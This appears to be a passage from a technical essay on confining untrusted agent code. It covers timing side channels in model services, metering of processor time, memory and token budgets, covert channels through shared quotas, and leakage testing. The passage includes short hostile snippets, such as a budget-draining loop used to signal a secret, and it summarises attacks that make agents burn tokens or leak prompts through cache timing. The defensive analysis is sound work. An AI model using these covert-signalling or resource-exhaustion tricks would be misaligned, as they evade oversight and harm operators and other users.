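A bound on total leakage doesn't protect every secret equally. *Tail Victims in Termination Timing Channel Defenses beyond Cryptographic Kernels* (Wei, Harris and colleagues) tests a version of the defence that doubles the release time whenever a program misses it. An attacker tried to identify which of 200 websites a browser had loaded from the loading time alone. With the defence on, the right site was among the attacker's first three guesses 10.7% of the time on average, but for nearly 9% of the sites the attacker succeeded more than 90% of the time.

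The defence is weakest at the boundary between release times. A site that takes 7.9 seconds appears after 8 seconds, while one that takes 8.1 appears after 16. The difference grows from 0.2 seconds to 8, which makes these two sites easier to tell apart. Smith's objection to average leakage also applies here.

Wei and colleagues found that random delays worked just as unevenly. A delay fitted to one graph-analysis program cut the attacker's success rate from 56.5% to 17%, but the same scheme left the rate at 41.5% for the browser.

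*Deterministically Deterring Timing Attacks in Deterland* notes that predictive mitigation also can't distinguish harmless variation from a leak, so it delays both. For a job like the contracts summary, one generous deadline is simpler and reveals less.

### Lipner's objection

Lipner had good reason in 1975 to expect that closing covert channels would add too much overhead. An account on Multicians, a site about the early operating system Multics, describes a demonstration in which one program signalled to another through the system's handling of memory. Closing that channel would have required extra bookkeeping and disk reads, and processor demand would have remained as another channel.

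Later measurements contradict Lipner's objection for programs that take turns on one processor core. Ge and colleagues closed most of those channels with an overhead of a few percent, and more efficient flush instructions would reduce it further. The objection still applies when programs run at the same time, because confinement then also prevents other domains from using some cores.

Wei and colleagues report that padding every run to its longest possible time causes tremendous overhead, except in cryptography, where running times vary little. The database system Fuzz shortened the padding by stopping slow queries early, but it still took 2.5 to 6 times as long, and its answers became less accurate.

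However, much of the work that agent code does can wait. If a summary takes 5 seconds and the operator holds the published list for 60, the wait is twelve times as long as the work, but that hardly matters to someone who reads the list the next morning. The processor can also sit idle during the wait, provided no other customer can see when it becomes idle. Lipner's objection is therefore much weaker for scheduled reports than for a chat service.

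### Timing in shared model services

Most programs written by agents also call language models, which create another timing channel. A model service can store its intermediate results for the beginning of a prompt in a prefix cache and reuse them when another prompt begins the same way, so the second reply starts sooner. If customers share the cache, one customer can infer from a fast reply that somebody else recently sent the same text.

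*Mirage* (2026) reviews research in which timing differences were enough to recover other users' prompts, and an audit that could detect reuse in commercial services from outside. Contracts are a natural target because many follow standard forms, so someone who knows the form may have to guess only a name or a price.

Services have several ways to limit the leak:

- They can give each customer a separate cache. This stops customers from affecting each other's timing through the cache, but they no longer benefit from prompts they have in common.
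- They can isolate only part of the cache. *CacheSolidarity* (2026) watches for suspicious reuse between customers and separates the affected beginnings, without analysing what the prompts mean. *Selective KV-Cache Sharing to Mitigate Timing Side-Channels in LLM Inference* (2025) also proposes sharing only some of the stored results.
- They can disguise the timing. *Mirage* leaves sensitive text in the shared cache and obscures the timing of replies once it detects a pattern typical of probing.

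Separate caches give the strongest protection because they don't rely on recognising an attack. The other methods keep more of caching's speed benefit but may miss someone who probes slowly or from many accounts. For confidential contracts, the operator should ask the provider for a separate cache and find out whether it covers every model the program can call.

If the provider offers none, the operator can have the object through which the program calls the model put the same long random string at the start of every prompt. Nobody else can then reproduce the beginning, but the operator's own prompts can still share stored results. The program must not know the string, because it could pass it to an accomplice and then signal through which prompts it leaves in the cache.

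Besides cache attacks, *Mirage* lists other timing attacks on these services. Some use the sizes of successive pieces of an encrypted reply, and others use variations in speed caused by methods that make models faster. An operator can avoid the first kind by requesting the whole reply at once instead of word by word, but anyone watching the network can still see its total length.

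## Metering processor time, memory and outside services

A program doesn't need any capabilities to stop everything around it. This line is enough:

```js
while (true) {}
```

If the contracts program runs this loop in the same thread as the operator's code, the operator's code never runs again. A timer meant to stop the program after ten seconds won't help, because the timer's code has to wait for the same thread. A loop that keeps adding items to a list does similar damage by using up memory. According to Miller, the most common threat to availability is the exhaustion of a resource that others need.

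The operator therefore needs to meter the program from outside and stop it when it has used up its budget.

### Caps and guaranteed shares

An operating system's scheduler can interrupt one thread to run another, but it can't help a function that is waiting for another function in the same thread to return, because stopping the thread would stop both. Boundaries can therefore protect availability only between separate threads, so the documentation of Hardened JavaScript suggests combining its compartments with process or worker boundaries. The threads should not share locks, because the scheduler may pause one thread while it holds a lock that another needs.

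Capping one program's processor time does not guarantee time for another. Ten programs that may each use 20% of a processor can together demand twice as much time as it has. An eleventh program may wait a long time even though none of the others has exceeded its cap. To guarantee it 10%, the scheduler must provide that much whenever the program is ready to run, and the guaranteed shares must total no more than 100%.

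Linux has separate settings for caps and shares. For a group of processes, `cpu.max` caps processor time, and `cpu.weight` sets the group's share relative to other groups when the processor is busy. `memory.max` caps the group's memory, and `memory.min` protects an amount that the system will not take away to give to others.

For the contracts program, the operator needs to set a cap for the agent code and a guaranteed share for the operator's own code. The operator's code publishes the list of categories at the deadline and stops the job, and the guaranteed share lets it run on time however busy the agent code is.

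### Three ways to limit processor time

A runtime can count a program's instructions, check a shared clock at intervals, or stop the program at a deadline. Most published measurements of the first two methods concern WebAssembly, a code format that browsers and servers run in a sandbox.

Blockchains call their instruction budget "gas". Esper, Freitas and colleagues (2026), in *Enabling Real-Time Programmability for RAN Functions*, explain how gas works for WebAssembly. Each instruction uses a fixed amount of gas. Before the program starts, the runtime inserts code that subtracts these amounts from the budget as the program runs, and the program stops when the budget runs out. Wasmtime, a widely used WebAssembly runtime, has a similar mechanism called fuel.

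Wasmtime's alternative to fuel is epoch interruption. Another thread increases a shared counter at regular intervals, for example every millisecond. The program compares the counter with its limit at the start of each function and each time it repeats a loop. The program only reads this counter, whereas fuel requires it to keep writing a new total.

An operator can also run the program in its own process and have the operating system kill the process at a deadline. This needs no extra code inside the program.

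| Method | What it measures | Does the program always stop at the same point? | Slowdown |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fuel or gas | Instructions | Yes, if its inputs are the same | 24–34% in 2022 tests |
| Epochs | Elapsed time, checked at loops and function calls | No | About 10–14% |
| Deadline for a process | Elapsed time | No | Almost none |

The fuel figures come from small benchmarks that the developer pepyakin ran on Wasmtime. Counting fuel without stopping the program still added 10–25% overhead. A Wasmtime maintainer explained in the same discussion that most of this overhead came from repeatedly loading and storing the counter. An experimental version that kept the counter in a processor register reduced the overhead to about 5%, but it left out the checks that stop the program.

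Wasmtime's *Interrupting Wasm Execution* puts the slowdown from epoch checks at around 10%. In a 2026 proposal, the developer erikrose reported a slowdown of 14.4% for SpiderMonkey, a JavaScript engine compiled to WebAssembly. The proposal replaces the comparison in each check with a bare memory read that triggers an interruption when the epoch ends. This reduced the slowdown to 2.8%, not counting the time taken by the interruptions. In a related discussion with fitzgen, another developer found that programs ran about 2–15% faster with epoch checks turned off.

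Epochs and fuel also make compiled programs larger. *Add epoch-based interruption* (cfallin, 2022), which introduced epochs, reports that a compiled copy of SpiderMonkey grew from 54 MB to 62 MB with epochs and to 68 MB with fuel. Larger programs take longer to compile, and an attacker can exploit this. Near One's *replacing nears contract vm with wasmtime* (2026) describes the problem on the NEAR blockchain, which inserts a check at each boundary between straight-line sequences of instructions. Compiling a hostile program with a huge number of these boundaries uses a lot of processor time before the program's first instruction runs, so the operator also needs to limit code size and compile time.

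Fuel's extra overhead is justified when several parties must agree on exactly where a program stopped. Blockchains need this because many computers repeat the same calculation. Fuel also suits the formatter that has no clock, since the load on the machine can't change where the formatter stops. Dayal (2025), in *Batched fuel consumption*, asked whether Wasmtime could add up the instructions in a block and subtract the total at once. A maintainer recalled that it already did so, but had to update the count before any operation with side effects, such as writing to memory, because the count would otherwise be wrong if the program stopped there.

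Fuel doesn't measure time, however. According to Crabbox, a project that uses Wasmtime's fuel count for testing, the count doesn't depend on the processor model or the load on the machine, so the same amount of fuel can last longer on a slow machine. Fuel also covers only the program's own instructions, and a single call to the host could start an hour of work outside the sandbox. The host has to meter or limit each such call separately.

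Deadlines have the opposite weakness. If the contracts program waits 55 seconds for documents, a 60-second deadline leaves it only five seconds to work on them. But a program with eight threads could use up to 480 seconds of processor time before the same deadline. The operator can set a separate limit on processor time, which doesn't count the time the program spends waiting.

These limits apply to each run separately, so an agent that restarts its program after each failure could get a full allowance every time. *TrustMee* (2026), which uses fuel to limit verification code that an attacker may have supplied, notes that a real service may also need to control repeated runs.

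### Memory and who is using it

A program can release memory, unlike processor time, so a memory limit applies to the amount it holds at any moment. A small program that holds its memory for a week may inconvenience others more than a large one that finishes in a minute. Some operators therefore also charge for how long a program holds memory.

The simplest limit applies to a whole sandbox. A WebAssembly program requests more memory from its runtime, which can refuse. An operating system can similarly limit a process's memory. Setting a separate limit for each program is harder when they share a JavaScript process. If one program creates a large object, gives a reference to a second program and then drops its own, only the second program keeps the object in memory. The runtime could count the object against the first program's limit, but that program can no longer free it. If the runtime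 counted it against the second program's limit instead, any program could use up another's limit by sending it large objects.

Linux has the same difficulty when several groups of processes share memory. It generally charges each page to the group that used it first, even if other groups use it more later.

A limit on the contracts program also doesn't cover memory that a service uses on the program's behalf. A 5 MB document may expand to 2 GB while the conversion service decodes it. The program stays within its own limit, but the service may reach its limit and crash, which interrupts every other client's work. The service could refuse large documents, but a document's size doesn't reliably predict how much memory the conversion will need.

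A service can run a separate process for each client and give each process its own memory limit. A document that needs too much memory then stops only that client's work. However, each process takes time to start and uses some memory even when idle.

### Resource containers and charging the caller

In 1999 Gaurav Banga, Peter Druschel and Jeffrey Mogul proposed a way to track each client's resource use without giving each client its own process. They argued that operating systems used the process both to keep programs out of one another's memory and to track resource use. On a web server, one process may serve thousands of clients, and a single request may involve several processes and a lot of work in the kernel.

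Their solution was a resource container, an account for everything the system uses to carry out one activity. A server handles a request like this:

1. The server creates a container for a client, or for a group of clients, and sets its limits.
2. When a thread starts work for that client, the server binds the thread to the container.
3. The kernel charges the thread's processor time to the container, along with the work of handling the client's network traffic.
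4. When the thread turns to another client, the server binds it to that client's container.

Containers can be nested, so a company can have a total limit with smaller limits for its departments. In one test, the researchers limited programs that generated pages on demand to 30% of the processor, and the server's output of ordinary pages stayed nearly constant however many of those programs were running.

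With containers, the conversion service could charge the contracts program for the processor time its documents need, provided the service binds its threads correctly. A careless service could charge one client for another's work, and the kernel could not detect the mistake. Shared results are also difficult to charge. If the service caches a converted document and five clients use it, the service needs a policy for dividing the charge among them.

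### Resources as capabilities

Resource containers add accounting to a system in which any program may run. Some capability systems instead treat processor time and storage as objects that a program must be granted, so even a program that only loops forever needs a capability to run.

KeyKOS limited processor time with meters and storage with space banks. A program could run only if it had a meter with time left. Meters formed a tree, and the time a program used also counted against the meters above its own. A parent could therefore stop everything below it by withdrawing one meter. A space bank supplied storage in the same way. Its holder could create a smaller bank with a limit and give it to another program, and destroying that bank recovered all the storage it had supplied.

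A customer who asked a KeyKOS factory for a new confined program supplied the meter and the space bank for it. The program ran on the customer's resources, so its author didn't need to set any aside for strangers.

The seL4 kernel uses capabilities to control memory by requiring programs to supply the memory for new kernel objects. For example, a program can create a thread only if it has a capability to unused memory. One program therefore can't exhaust a shared pool of kernel memory.

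seL4 later added control over processor time through scheduling-context capabilities, which Anna Lyons and colleagues presented in 2018. A scheduling context has a budget and a period, such as 10 milliseconds in every 100. A thread with this context gets at most 10% of a processor core, and a thread with no scheduling context can't run. Setting the budget and period requires a separate capability, so a program without it can't increase its own budget.

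Scheduling contexts also let a system count a service's processor time against its callers. A service can wait for calls with no processor time of its own, and a client that calls it lends it a scheduling context until the reply. If the conversion service worked this way, converting a long document would use up the contracts program's time. If the budget runs out in the middle of a request, the kernel can notify a handler, which might lend the service enough extra time to finish, or cancel the request and restore the service to a usable state.

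With these designs, an operator can see which programs may use processor time or storage by looking at their grants, can divide these resources among programs, and can take them back. A program can't increase its share by copying the reference, because both copies lead to the same meter. If a budget were only a number in a message, three recipients could each try to use the full amount.

A trusted component still has to measure usage. In KeyKOS and seL4, this is the kernel, which needs a reliable clock and has to interrupt a thread when its budget runs out. The capability also doesn't ensure that the budget is sensible. In seL4, a scheduling context sets an upper limit on a thread's processor time, and threads with higher priority run first. To guarantee a low-priority thread a share, whoever hands out the contexts has to check that the other threads' budgets leave enough time for it.

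### Budgets for calls, tokens and money

A machine's kernel can't measure the resources that outside services use. A program may use almost no processor time while it waits for a language model whose replies cost several dollars. The contracts program needs separate limits on the number of calls, the number of tokens (the units of text that model providers charge for), and the money it spends. Limiting calls doesn't limit tokens, since one call may use a thousand times as many as another, and limiting tokens doesn't limit spending if the program can choose among models with different prices.

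A program or agent may also pass work to others. The rule is then that a parent's own spending plus the budgets it gives its children must never exceed the parent's budget. If the parent has a budget *B*, spends *s* itself and gives its children *b₁*, …, *bₙ*, then

*s* + *b₁* + … + *bₙ* ≤ *B*.

If every child follows the same rule, the total stays within *B* however many generations there are.

Each call needs to follow the rule too, although nobody knows its exact cost in advance. The budget can handle this in three steps:

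1. Before the call, reserve the most it could cost. Refuse the call if that amount isn't available.
2. Send the request with a limit on the length of the reply, so that it can't cost more than the reservation.
3. When the reply arrives, refund the difference between the reservation and the actual cost.

The following object applies both rules to a paid service:

```js
function makeMeteredService(service, limit) {
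  let left = limit;
  function take(amount) {
    if (!Number.isSafeInteger(amount) || amount <= 0 || amount > left) {
      throw new Error('Invalid amount or not enough budget');
    }
    left -= amount;
  }
  return harden({
    split(amount) {
      take(amount);
      return makeMeteredService(service, amount);
    },
    async send(request, maxCost) {
      take(maxCost);
      const { body, cost } = await service.send(request, maxCost);
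      left += maxCost - cost;
      return body;
    },
  });
}
```

The operator gives the agent code this object and keeps the underlying service private. The service must treat `maxCost` as a strict limit and report the true cost. If a call fails without reporting a cost, the full reserved amount counts as spent.

The check on `amount` matters because a negative number would increase the budget. *Concordat* (2026), which presents a library for agents that pass work to one another, reports that an early version accepted negative amounts, so a parent could increase its own budget by giving a child a negative allowance. The corrected version subtracts each child's allowance from its parent's and doesn't allow a child unlimited use of any resource that is limited for the parent.

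*Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) describes another arrangement, in which the runtime counts every use of a resource toward the totals of the program and all its ancestors. Child programs can then use what their siblings leave unused, but the runtime has to check several shared totals at each call.

### A small task that makes 121 calls

Delegation can multiply costs very quickly. Suppose that each call uses 10,000 tokens and makes three more calls, down to four levels below the first:

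| Level | Calls | Tokens at this level | Budget needed by each call and everything below it |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 1 | 10,000 | 1,210,000 |
| 1 | 3 | 30,000 | 400,000 |
| 2 | 9 | 90,000 | 130,000 |
| 3 | 27 | 270,000 | 40,000 |
| 4 | 81 | 810,000 | 10,000 |
| Total | 121 | 1,210,000 | |

A cap of 10,000 tokens per call wouldn't prevent any of this, because every call stays within it. Limiting the depth helps, but allowing one more level would still bring the total to 364 calls and 3.64 million tokens.

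Now suppose that the first call has a budget of 300,000 tokens and divides what it doesn't need equally among its three children, which do the same. It uses 10,000 and gives each child about 96,700. Each child uses 10,000 and gives each of its own three children about 28,900. After those nine calls use 10,000 each, only about 6,300 tokens are available for each further call, which is less than the 10,000 it needs. The task stops after 13 calls and 130,000 tokens, with 170,000 unused.

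A single shared budget of 300,000 tokens would allow 30 calls, but one branch might use them all. Equal shares protect the branches from one another but leave small amounts unused in separate branches. A reasonable compromise is for branches to return unused tokens to the parent, which can give them to any branch that still has useful work to do.

### How agents have overspent

*Token Budgets* (Khan, 2026) lists 63 confirmed budget overruns reported on GitHub between 2023 and 2026. One user reported about $2,150 in unintended spending, and another spent $235 in four days. The full collection has 110 entries, including missing features and requests for budget controls. Across those entries, retry loops were the most common cause, with 27 entries, and 11 involved work that agents had passed to other agents. Two people classifying the causes agreed only moderately, so these counts are approximate.

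The same problems occur in many independently written systems in Khan's collection. Khan searched for projects with signs of budget trouble, so the collection can't show how often agents overspend.

An outsider can also make an agent use far more resources than a task needs. In *Beyond Max Tokens*, Zhou, Zheng and colleagues (2026) ran a controlled simulation in which a malicious tool led agents through long series of unnecessary calls before returning the right answer. With Llama 3.3 70B, average output for one set of tasks rose from 260 tokens per request to 81,830. The agent still succeeded in 96.2% of cases, compared with 98.1% with the benign tool, so a user who looked only at the answers would rarely have noticed.

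The increase ranged from about 66 to 658 times across six models and two sets of tasks. The attack also used 100 to 560 times as much energy and filled 35% to 74% of the memory the model server keeps for ongoing conversations. On a shared server, this leaves less memory for other users.

Each reply in these tests could contain at most 16,384 tokens. No reply exceeded that limit, but an agent that makes *n* calls can produce up to *n* times that many tokens, and only a budget for the whole task would have limited the total.

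*Clawdrain* (2026) lists related attacks, including ones that make a model do unnecessary hidden reasoning or make an agent repeat irrelevant actions. Agents can also overload a shared service when no one is attacking it, as they did with the package service in OpenAI's 2026 incident.

### Limits in current agent runtimes

Many agent runtimes limit something that is easier to count than money:

| Limit | What it counts | What can still grow |
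|---|---|---|
| `recursion_limit` in LangGraph, `max_iter` in CrewAI, `max_turns` in AutoGen | Steps or turns | The cost of each step |
| A model provider's maximum reply length | Output tokens in one reply | The number of replies |
| A budget in the LiteLLM proxy, as Khan tested it | Money, after each call | The cost of the call that crosses the limit |
| The budget in *Concordat* | Tokens, tool calls and dollars | Dollars, if the application doesn't report them |

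Khan tested the three step counters, the LiteLLM proxy and a cost-tracking add-on with a task that kept retrying and a spending limit of $0.02. All five let spending exceed the limit in all 30 runs. Khan's own library, which reserves the cost before each call, never did. The 30 runs were almost identical, so they are better treated as one demonstration for each tool. In a more varied test of 160 runs, the library again kept spending within its limit.

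The designers of the step counters never meant them to limit spending, so the comparison is a little unfair. Khan included them because people use them for that purpose anyway. In another test, with a limit of about half a cent, some step counters let spending reach almost 14 times the limit.

Reserving the cost in advance leaves some of the budget unused. Khan's standard method reserves four to six times the actual cost. In a trial with 40 tasks and a limit of $0.05, the library allowed 22 and refused 18 after spending $0.0404. The average task had cost less than $0.002, but a typical reservation was about $0.0104, more than the $0.0096 left. Asking the provider to count the tokens first makes the reservation almost exact, but adds about one to two seconds to each call.

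The limit also depends on the provider respecting the maximum reply length, reporting usage truthfully and keeping its prices the same during the task. According to Khan, the first condition fails for some reasoning models, because their providers also charge for hidden reasoning that the maximum doesn't cover. For these models, the operator also needs the provider's own limit on reasoning.

The limit on outgoing requests in Cloudflare's *Dynamic Workers* has a similar gap, because a request to an expensive model counts the same as a request for a small web page. To limit spending, the operator has to put a budget in the object through which the program calls the model.

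### When several calls pass the same check

A budget can fail even though every program checks it. Three agents may each ask whether there is enough money, get the answer "yes" and make a call before any of them has recorded its spending. Khan reproduced this with three simultaneous calls, each of which had an estimated cost of 31 units and an actual cost of 23:

| Arrangement | Budget | Calls allowed | Total cost |
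|---|---|---|---|
| Shared budget, checked before the call and reduced afterwards | 60 | 3 | 69 |
| Shared budget, with a lock and a reservation | 60 | 1 | 23 |
| Budget divided equally among the agents | 60 | 0 | 0 |
| Budget divided equally among the agents | 100 | 3 | 69 |

Only the first arrangement exceeded its budget. The lock prevented other agents from acting between the check and the reservation. After one call reserved 31 of the 60 units, the remaining 29 were too few for either of the other two calls. The refund left 37 units available, so one of the refused agents could have retried successfully. Dividing the 60 units equally gave each agent 20, which wasn't enough for any call.

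In Khan's library, splitting a budget uses up the original, and the Rust compiler rejects a program that tries to use the original again. A correctly locked counter enforces the limit just as well. But the compiler's check doesn't depend on the programmer remembering to add a lock, which is useful when a model writes the code.

The `makeMeteredService` object avoids the problem because `take` checks the budget and reduces it without waiting between the two steps. JavaScript runs only one piece of code at a time in each thread, so no other call can run between them. This protection does not extend beyond a single process. Cloudflare warns that two requests to the same loaded program may reach different copies of it, each with its own memory. A counter in that memory would give every copy the full budget. The operator should keep the total in one durable place outside the program, as with the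 disclosure ledger.

### When a limit stops work halfway

A limit can stop a program partway through its work. The contracts program might have written half a section of the summary, or sent a document for conversion and not yet received the result. Wasmtime can end a program that reaches its limit, or pause it so the host can decide whether to continue. Pausing preserves the work, but the operator still needs a plan for programs that never finish.

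Blockchains usually solve this by undoing everything the transaction did and keeping the fee. That works because all the transaction's effects are inside the blockchain's own records. The operator can do something similar with the contracts program's summary file by having the program write to a temporary copy. The operator's code replaces the real file only once the copy is complete.

No runtime can undo an email or a paid conversion. Zhang's runtime therefore saves a record of what it is about to do, and reserves the cost, before it contacts an outside service. After a crash, it acts according to what this record shows:

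- If the request definitely never left, the runtime returns the reservation.
- If the request may have left, the runtime treats the result as unknown. It charges the full reservation unless it has a better measurement, and doesn't send the request again automatically.
- If the service can confirm what happened, for instance with a receipt, an adapter written for that service can use this to settle the record.

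If the program records a charge when the conversion company sends no reply, it may charge for a conversion that never took place. Treating a missing reply as failure is worse, because the program may order and pay for the same conversion many times. Giving each job a unique number helps, provided the company recognises a repeated number and returns the existing result.

Cleaning up also uses resources. If the program has used its whole budget, it can't cancel a job or write a final message. The operator should reserve a separate amount for cleanup and give it to trusted code, because agent code could use it for more work.

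The budget should also cover the whole task, so that it doesn't reset with each new attempt. At up to 10,000 tokens per contract, summarising all 120 contracts takes at most 1.2 million tokens. If the program starts from the beginning on each of its 20 permitted attempts, it could use 24 million. A task budget of 1.5 million leaves enough to repeat the work on 30 contracts, which allows for occasional failures if the program saves each finished section and continues from there.

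## Combining the mechanisms and testing the result

A token budget keeps the contracts program from overspending, but it also gives the program a new way to signal. This code wastes the whole budget as soon as the program finds a penalty clause:

```js
if (contract.includes('penalty')) {
  while (true) await model.send(filler, 10000);
}
```

The loop ends when the meter rejects a call. The stopping point then reveals which contract is the first with a penalty clause, as it did after the mistake with `flagged`. Non-malicious code also leaks information this way, though less precisely, because long contracts use more tokens than short ones.

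### Leaks through limits

How much leaks depends on what the observer can see. For a budget of 1.5 million tokens and a folder of 120 contracts, counting the possible outcomes gives these bounds:

| What the observer sees | Possible outcomes | Most it can reveal |
|---|---|---|
| The exact number of tokens used | 1,500,001 | 20.5 bits |
| The number of contracts finished | 121 | 6.9 bits |
| A bill rounded up to the next 100,000 tokens | 16 | 4 bits |
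| Whether the run finished | 2 | 1 bit |

Outsiders who read only the published list of categories learn nothing extra from the meter, because the 360 bits already counted for the list allow for the case in which the meter stops the run.

The bill is harder to hide. Accounts staff may see it without being allowed to see the contracts, so the operator should show them a rounded figure. To make the real bill constant, the operator would have to spend the unused tokens on pointless calls. If a typical task needs 1.2 million tokens, these calls add 25% to its cost.

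A program doesn't leak its secrets through its resource use if that use doesn't depend on them. *Verifying and Synthesizing Constant-Resource Implementations with Types* (2018) presents a type system that checks for this, assuming an attacker who sees the program's public outputs and its final resource consumption. Compilation can still undo the guarantee. The method suits small functions better than a program that calls a language model, because the length of the model's replies varies.

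Retries add to the leak. A program that gets a fresh budget each time it runs out can leak one bit per attempt by choosing which attempts fail, as with the untracked retry loop that Garby and colleagues found in CaMeL. This is another reason to give all attempts one shared budget and a single deadline.

Timing defences can also make a program exceed its time limit. Suppose the program makes one model call per contract, and calls take 3 seconds on average and 8 at most. Without padding, the 120 calls take about 6 minutes. If the runtime pads every call to 8 seconds, they take 16 minutes. With a 10-minute limit, the padded program always stops after 75 contracts, so the stopping point reveals nothing, but the remaining 45 contracts have no summary.

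Padding once, by holding the finished result until the deadline, uses fewer resources than padding repeatedly. That wait should not count against the program's time limit. The operator's code can also save the result and end the process early to free its memory, provided nobody outside can see the memory become free.

### Fixed shares and shared pools

Any shared pool can carry signals, as the conversion service's page quota can. If branches of a task return unused tokens to their parent, a branch that has read the contracts can signal to another branch by how many tokens it returns.

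Suppose the contracts program and another customer's program share a limit of 100 page conversions an hour. Each request is for one page, and unused conversions and refused requests do not carry over to the next hour.

| Pages requested | Hour 1 | Hour 2 | Hour 3 | Hour 4 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Contracts program | 80 | 20 | 90 | 10 |
| Other program | 20 | 70 | 10 | 60 |

With a shared pool, the service converts all 360 pages. But the other program can keep requesting pages until the service refuses, and the number it gets can take 101 values, so it can leak up to 6.7 bits an hour. If each program instead has a fixed share of 50 pages, nothing leaks through the quota, but the service refuses 100 requests while 140 pages go unused.

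As a compromise, trusted code can check the demand each hour and choose one of three splits: 25/75, 50/50 or 75/25. The other program can then learn only which split applies.

| Arrangement | Pages converted | Most the other program can learn in four hours |
|---|---|---|
| Shared pool | 360 | 26.6 bits |
| One of three splits each hour | 340 | 6.3 bits |
| Fixed halves | 260 | 0 bits |

Here the compromise recovers most of the lost capacity with about a quarter of the leak. The result depends on demand, so an operator should repeat the calculation with real figures.

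A first-come, first-served queue can carry a covert message between users. The receiver submits a steady stream of small jobs and measures the gaps between their completions. Each extra time slot in a gap means that somebody else's job came in between. Ghassami and Kiyavash (2017), in *A Covert Queueing Channel in FCFS Schedulers*, proved that this channel can carry 0.8114 bits per slot when two users share a server and all jobs are the same size. At one job per second, that is enough to send a 128-bit key in under three minutes. Documents of different lengths and jobs from other customers would add noise.

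Fixed time slots close the timing channel. Kadloor, Kiyavash and Venkitasubramaniam (2013), in *Mitigating Timing Side Channel in Shared Schedulers*, showed that an observer then does no better than someone who knows only the other user's average rate. However, fixed slots reduce throughput and increase delays, especially with many users. Serving jobs in batches is a compromise, but Gong, Kiyavash and Venkitasubramaniam (2013), in *An Information Theoretic Study of Timing Side Channels in Two-user Schedulers*, found that batching gives the most privacy only with large delays.

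Lending out idle slots only halves the nearly complete leak that occurs when the other user submits few jobs, according to Gong and Kiyavash (2014) in *Quantifying the Information Leakage in Timing Side Channels in Deterministic Work-Conserving Schedulers*. They proved that no deterministic scheduler can do better if it never idles while a job is waiting. Closing the channel therefore requires wasting some capacity.

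### Comparing paired runs

These calculations cover only channels that somebody has thought of. To look for others, the operator can run the code twice with the same public inputs and different secrets, which turns the definition of noninterference into an experiment:

1. Write down what counts as public. If outsiders may know how many contracts there are but not how long they are, the two test folders need the same number of contracts with different lengths.
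2. Fill the folders with invented contracts that differ sharply. One might contain penalty clauses, a very long document and a document that makes the program fail.
3. Run the program several times on the same folder to see how much the results vary anyway.
4. Run it on both folders in random order, using a fresh sandbox each time. Keep the code, budget, model version and random seed the same within each pair, and change the seed between pairs.
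5. Record what each observer could see, and compare the two folders.
6. Repeat the test with code that leaks on purpose, to check that the test can detect a leak.

| What to compare | What a difference may mean |
|---|---|
| Outputs | Their text, order or length depends on a secret |
| Number and size of calls to each service | The program chooses its requests according to what it reads |
| Errors and refusals | A limit or a label check stopped only one of the runs |
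| Completion times | An output escapes the fixed deadline |
| Processor time, memory, tokens and remaining quota | A bill or a shared pool could reveal the secret |

The third step matters because agents' behaviour can change for trivial reasons. In *Attributing Security Outcomes in LLM-Agent Evaluations*, Bounite and Iklassov (2026) ran one agent through 400 simulated attacks twice, changing only a random seed that affected the order of its tools, and the outcome changed in 59 cases. Reruns with the same seed were identical. An operator who always used one seed would therefore never notice this variation, and one who changed the seed between the two runs of a pair might mistake the variation for a leak.

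Bounite and Iklassov also checked whether their tests could detect a planted effect of three percentage points. A test that averaged over six tool orders detected it in all 2,000 simulated repeats, while a standard test on single runs detected it 29.5% of the time. *AgentSecBench* (2026) similarly pairs its attacks with controls and estimates the attacker's advantage.

Failed runs can be mistaken for successful defenses. In one of Bounite and Iklassov's tests, the model server rejected every request, and the benchmark reported that no attack had succeeded. The operator should count failed runs separately and check whether they are more common with one folder than with another, since that difference would itself be a leak.

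### Estimating a channel's capacity

Once a test finds a difference, the operator needs to know how much information that difference can carry. A channel's capacity is the largest Shannon leakage that any choice of input probabilities can produce.

To estimate it for completion times, the operator can write a program that finishes quickly to send a 0 and slowly to send a 1. Half of the runs serve to choose the time that best separates the two, and the other half show how often the receiver gets the bit wrong. If both bits have the same error rate *e*, the capacity is

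1 + *e* log₂ *e* + (1 − *e*) log₂(1 − *e*) bits per run.

With 20 errors in 200 runs, *e* is 0.1 and the capacity is about 0.53 bits per attempt. Over 20 visible attempts, the channel could carry about 10.6 bits.

This method can never show more than one bit per run because the sender uses only two signals, so the operator should also try several durations. With more signals, a small sample can make the leakage look too high. To see how much of the apparent leakage comes from chance, the operator can shuffle the record of which signal the program sent in each run and repeat the calculation.

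A better sender or receiver might transmit more information, so the estimate is closer to a minimum than a maximum. Counting the possible outcomes gives the maximum, which was 15.9 bits for a release at any millisecond within a minute. When the estimate and the maximum are this far apart, the ledger should record the maximum.

### What a clean result proves

Suppose that each run leaks with probability *p*, independently of the others. The chance of seeing no leak in *n* runs is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. Setting this equal to 0.05 gives the highest leak rate that is still consistent with a clean result at 95% confidence:

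*p* = 1 − 0.05^(1/*n*) ≈ 3/*n*.

For the 131 trials in which TACIT leaked no wrapped secrets, the bound is about 2.3%. This is optimistic because Odersky and colleagues used the same 12 tasks in 120 of the trials. If trials of the same task always had the same result, there would be only 23 independent trials (the 12 tasks and 11 requests for secrets), and the bound would be about 12%.

More runs lower the bound, and about 3,000 clean ones would bring it to 0.1%. But the bound applies only to attacks like those in the test. Hostile code could be written to leak only when a contract names a particular company, and a test with invented contracts would probably never trigger the leak. An attacker who finds one input that works can reuse it, however rare such inputs were among the test cases.

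A proof of noninterference compares pairs of runs, so it needs an adequate model of both, and a tool's code doesn't show which inputs an agent will choose. *PACE* (2026), which describes a system that checks agents' tool calls, therefore uses noninterference as a standard for comparison and doesn't claim to achieve it. An operator can avoid part of the difficulty of modeling runs by proving properties of the runtime that hold for any program.

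### What the seL4 proof covers

*seL4* (2013), by Murray, Matichuk and colleagues, proves a form of noninterference for the 8,830 lines of C in the seL4 kernel. The proof covers a system divided into partitions, with a policy that sets which partitions may send information to which others. It assumes that all the programs in the partitions are hostile and cooperate. No sequence of instructions and kernel calls lets them learn another partition's secrets through memory, processor registers or other state in the model, unless the policy allows it.

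The kernel runs the partitions in a fixed order with fixed time slices, so one partition's demand can't affect when the next is due to run. The proof allows one-way communication between partitions through shared memory and simple notifications.

The result depends on several assumptions:

- The compiler, the hardware, 450 lines of assembly code and the code that starts the kernel are all correct.
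- Devices can't access memory directly, and programs check devices for new data because the kernel delivers no device interrupts to them.
- The initial setup matches the policy and keeps a spare copy of every capability that crosses between partitions.

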